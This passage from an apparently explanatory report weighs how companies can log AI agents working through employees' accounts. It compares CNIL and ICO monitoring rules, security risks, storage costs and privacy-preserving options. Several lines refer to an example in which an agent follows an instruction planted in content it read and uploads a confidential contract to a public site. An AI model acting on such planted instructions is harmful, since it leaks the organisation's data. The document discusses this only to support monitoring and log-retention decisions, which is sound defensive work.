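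The agent's own records contain less about unrelated activity, but they can still be personal. An employee might ask an agent to draft a note to a doctor or a complaint about a manager. Even if the text isn't recorded, the times of prompts show roughly when someone works. Anthropic suggests using the same events to compare costs by user, and a manager could easily use that comparison to judge performance.

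Metadata alone can be intrusive enough to break the law. In December 2023 the French data protection authority, CNIL, fined Amazon's French warehouse business €32 million, mainly for monitoring employees excessively. According to CNIL's *Employee monitoring* (2024), each worker had a scanner that recorded tasks such as shelving and packing in real time.

Records can also wrongly attribute an agent's actions to an employee. In *Employment practices and data protection* (2023), the UK's Information Commissioner's Office (ICO) requires employers to take reasonable steps to ensure that monitoring data isn't misleading. A log that names A. Rossi as the sender of an email the agent wrote could mislead a disciplinary panel. The ICO also advises employers to let workers see and challenge the results of monitoring.

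Giving the agent its own account and browser profile, or better, its own machine, would reduce all these problems. The company could then record the agent in detail and the employee much less.

### What data protection law requires in Europe

The European Union's *General Data Protection Regulation* (2016), or GDPR, covers any information about an identifiable person, so a metadata record with A. Rossi's email address is personal data. An employer needs a specific purpose and a legal basis for collecting it, may collect only what that purpose requires, and must tell employees about the collection. Member states can add their own rules for workplaces.

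CNIL's *Recommandation sur le déploiement d'un serveur mandataire web filtrant* (2026) gives some of the most detailed official advice on one of the four routes. It covers proxies that filter employees' web traffic and isn't binding. CNIL accepts that an employer can rely on its legitimate interest in security, after weighing it against employees' interests. The GDPR requires employers to keep data secure, but an employer can't call the proxy a legal obligation on that ground alone. The EU AI Act's logging duty is more explicit, but it will cover only high-risk systems.

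CNIL advises employers to carry out an impact assessment, a written study of the risks to people and how to reduce them, if at least two of these apply:

- the proxy collects sensitive or highly personal data
- it collects personal data on a large scale
- it affects vulnerable people
- it monitors people systematically

Under European guidelines, employees can count as vulnerable because their employer has power over them. A proxy that logs all staff traffic therefore probably already meets two of the criteria, as would most systems that record agents working through employees' accounts.

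UK law offers a useful but limited contrast, as it derives from the GDPR. The ICO separates what employers "must" do by law from what they "should" do as good practice.

| Question | CNIL, on web proxies | ICO, on monitoring workers |
|---|---|---|
| Purpose | Security, compliance or blocking forbidden sites, with no incompatible reuse | Employers must document it, and should not monitor "just in case" |
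| Necessity | Only the data that filtering and logging need | The least intrusive means |
| Notice | Individual notice, including which kinds of site the proxy doesn't decrypt | Required, except for covert monitoring in exceptional cases |
| Impact assessment | Advised if two criteria apply, and good practice otherwise | Required for likely high risk, and advised otherwise |
| Consultation | Advised even where the law doesn't require it | Advised, unless there is a good reason not to |
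| Keeping logs | Six months to a year, or longer with a documented reason | No fixed period, but the employer must be able to justify its choice |

French and British rules differ most on consulting workers. France's labour code, which CNIL cites, requires employers with a works council to consult it before they introduce ways of monitoring staff. In Britain, ICO advises employers that decide against consulting workers to record their reasons. ICO wrote this guidance before the Data (Use and Access) Act 2025, whose data protection provisions it says are now in force.

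Under these rules, a company can still keep detailed records of agents, for example by deciding in advance that it needs them to investigate unauthorised transfers and using them only for that. A permanent archive of every prompt, kept in case it proves useful, would be harder to justify. The ICO also prefers prevention where it is less intrusive. Its example is an employer that blocks certain websites so that it needs less monitoring. Similarly, a company could restrict the addresses to which an agent may upload files instead of reading every page its employees open.

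On 21 October 2026, EU governments agreed their position on amendments to the GDPR (Council of the EU, *Digital rulebook*, 2026). They want a single EU list of high-risk processing (Lewis Silkin, *Digital Rulebook*, 2026), which could make it clearer when agent monitoring needs an impact assessment. Negotiations with the European Parliament start only once it has agreed its own position (The Brussels Times, *New EU data rules promise simpler compliance but raise privacy concerns*).

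### The security cost of each route

CNIL warns that TLS inspection breaks a secure channel and exposes readable data on the proxy. It advises companies not to decrypt traffic to sites that pose no particular risk, such as those of banks, health services and public bodies. It also recommends requiring multi-factor login for administrators and restricting log access to authorised staff.

CNIL recommends that the proxy discard the content of decrypted requests unless it detects malicious code. The stolen contract contains none, so in step 5 the proxy would record the user, the time and at least part of the web address, but not the document. A company could keep more with a data-loss tool, which checks outgoing files, but CNIL's recommendation doesn't cover those tools.

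Endpoint sensors run with high privileges on every machine, so a single fault can quickly affect many of them. In July 2024 a faulty update to CrowdStrike's sensor crashed about 8.5 million Windows computers, by Microsoft's estimate. CNIL (2026) confirmed that its proxy recommendation does not cover endpoint detection and response, and planned a separate consultation on those services, according to Digital Watch's *French data protection authority sets out 2026 GDPR and AI guidance agenda*.

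A smaller French case shows that a device's records can be insecure even when the software works. On 19 December 2024 CNIL fined a property company €40,000 over software that tracked the activity of staff working from home and took screenshots, according to Botchorichvili, in *France*. Administrators shared one login, so the company couldn't trace who had looked at the data or what they had done with it. CNIL treated the shared login as a breach of the GDPR's security rules and the missing impact assessment as another breach, according to the law firm Arthur Cox. A larger business would probably have been fined more, since CNIL took the company's size and turnover into account (Lewis Silkin, 2025).

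Attackers can use a compromised browser extension to steal data from the organisations that installed it. In December 2024 they tricked an employee of Cyberhaven, which sells an extension for preventing data theft, into giving them access to the company's Chrome Web Store account. They published a malicious version of the extension that could steal cookies and login sessions, and Chrome's automatic updates delivered it to customers.

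When the agent software keeps the records, the risk lies in the log and the credentials that open it. Anyone with a key to a company's stored transcripts can read many employees' conversations without touching their laptops.

### An illustrative storage estimate

The money a company spends on storage depends mainly on whether it keeps text, and on how many copies. The estimate below is illustrative and rests on these assumptions:

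- 1,000 agents each work 250 days a year.
- Each agent makes 300 tool calls a day, in ten tasks of 30 calls.
- Each call produces three metadata records of 1 kilobyte, for the approval, the result and the request to the model.
- Each call adds 20 kilobytes of new text to the conversation, or about seven pages.

The number of calls is realistic for coding agents, since Elastic's log averages about 280 events per machine per working day. The text sizes are guesses. Together the agents make 75 million tool calls a year.

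| What the company keeps | Calculation | Storage for one year |
|---|---|---|
| Metadata only | 75 million × 3 kilobytes | 225 gigabytes |
| Metadata, with all new text once | 75 million × 23 kilobytes | 1.7 terabytes |
| Metadata, with every model request in full | 225 gigabytes + 2.5 million tasks × 9.3 megabytes | 23.5 terabytes |

The last row is much larger because the harness resends the conversation with each request. The request after the first tool call contains one 20-kilobyte block of text, the request after the second contains two, and so on up to 30. That makes 1 + 2 + ... + 30 = 465 blocks, or 9.3 megabytes, per task. If the agents made the same total number of calls in tasks twice as long, the figure in the last row would nearly double, while the other rows wouldn't change.

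Claude Code has a setting that writes full requests and replies to files, according to Panther, which sells software for analysing security logs. A company that uses this setting should remove the repeated text or at least compress it. Saving one 200-kilobyte screenshot per call would add 15 terabytes a year.

If storing a gigabyte for a year costs an assumed $1, the metadata would cost $225, the text stored once about $1,700, and the full requests $23,500. Real prices vary widely, and the time staff spend reviewing records would probably cost more than any of these. For a company with 1,000 agents, the price of storage is therefore a weak argument against keeping each text once, and privacy and security are much stronger ones.

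### Middle options and what each one loses

Redaction removes chosen details, such as passwords or names, before they are stored in the log. It works well for information with a fixed format, like a card number, but software can't easily recognise a confidential clause in a contract. Redaction can also remove evidence. If a rule deleted all web addresses from commands, the company wouldn't know where the contract went in step 5. If the filter runs at the collector, the unredacted text has already left the laptop.

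Hashes let a company check whether two files are identical without storing either. If the log held a hash of the uploaded file, an investigator could compare it with hashes of the company's contracts and find the supply agreement. The comparison fails for the summary in step 4 and for any file the agent has edited. Short values such as email addresses need a secret key mixed into the hash, or anyone could hash a list of likely addresses and look for a match.

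Hashing the names in a log doesn't exempt it from the GDPR. The EU governments' position would add an article on pseudonymised data, in which a code replaces a person's identity. Such data might not be personal data for an independent recipient who has no realistic way to identify anyone. According to Lewis Silkin, it can still be personal data for the company and for suppliers that process it on the company's behalf, which would normally include a monitoring vendor.

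Under short retention, an organisation keeps the full text for a limited time and the metadata for longer. In the estimate above, a year of metadata with 30 days of text would take up about 350 gigabytes, a fifth of the space needed to keep both for a year. However, some incidents are discovered late. The company in the example found its contract on a public website a month after the task, just after a 30-day log would have deleted the planted instruction. Anthropic found one of its incidents after seven months. It is therefore safer to keep the text for several months and to have a way to stop deletion once someone suspects a problem.

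Anthropic's default retention period for transcripts of local sessions is six years. That is at least six times as long as CNIL recommends for logs, so a French customer will probably have to justify it.

Sampling keeps the full text of only some tasks. Recording one task in a hundred would be enough to study how employees use agents, but the company would have only a 1% chance of holding the text of the task in which the contract left the company. Surapani and colleagues suggest choosing by risk instead, with full records for high-risk actions and summaries for the rest. But in step 5 the agent read the planted text before it did anything that looked risky, so the software would have to hold the whole conversation until the task ended, then keep or delete it.

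The company could make the text harder to misuse by requiring two people to open it. It could encrypt the text so that an investigator can open a conversation only with a second person, such as the data protection officer, and log each opening under both names. This would stop a curious administrator from reading colleagues' prompts, but it would also slow the response to an attack in progress. The company would still collect the same amount, so it would still have to show that it needs the text.

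Encrypting only certain fields would avoid some of the delay. Security staff could search recipients, destinations and file sizes by themselves, and would need the second person only to read the email or the contract.
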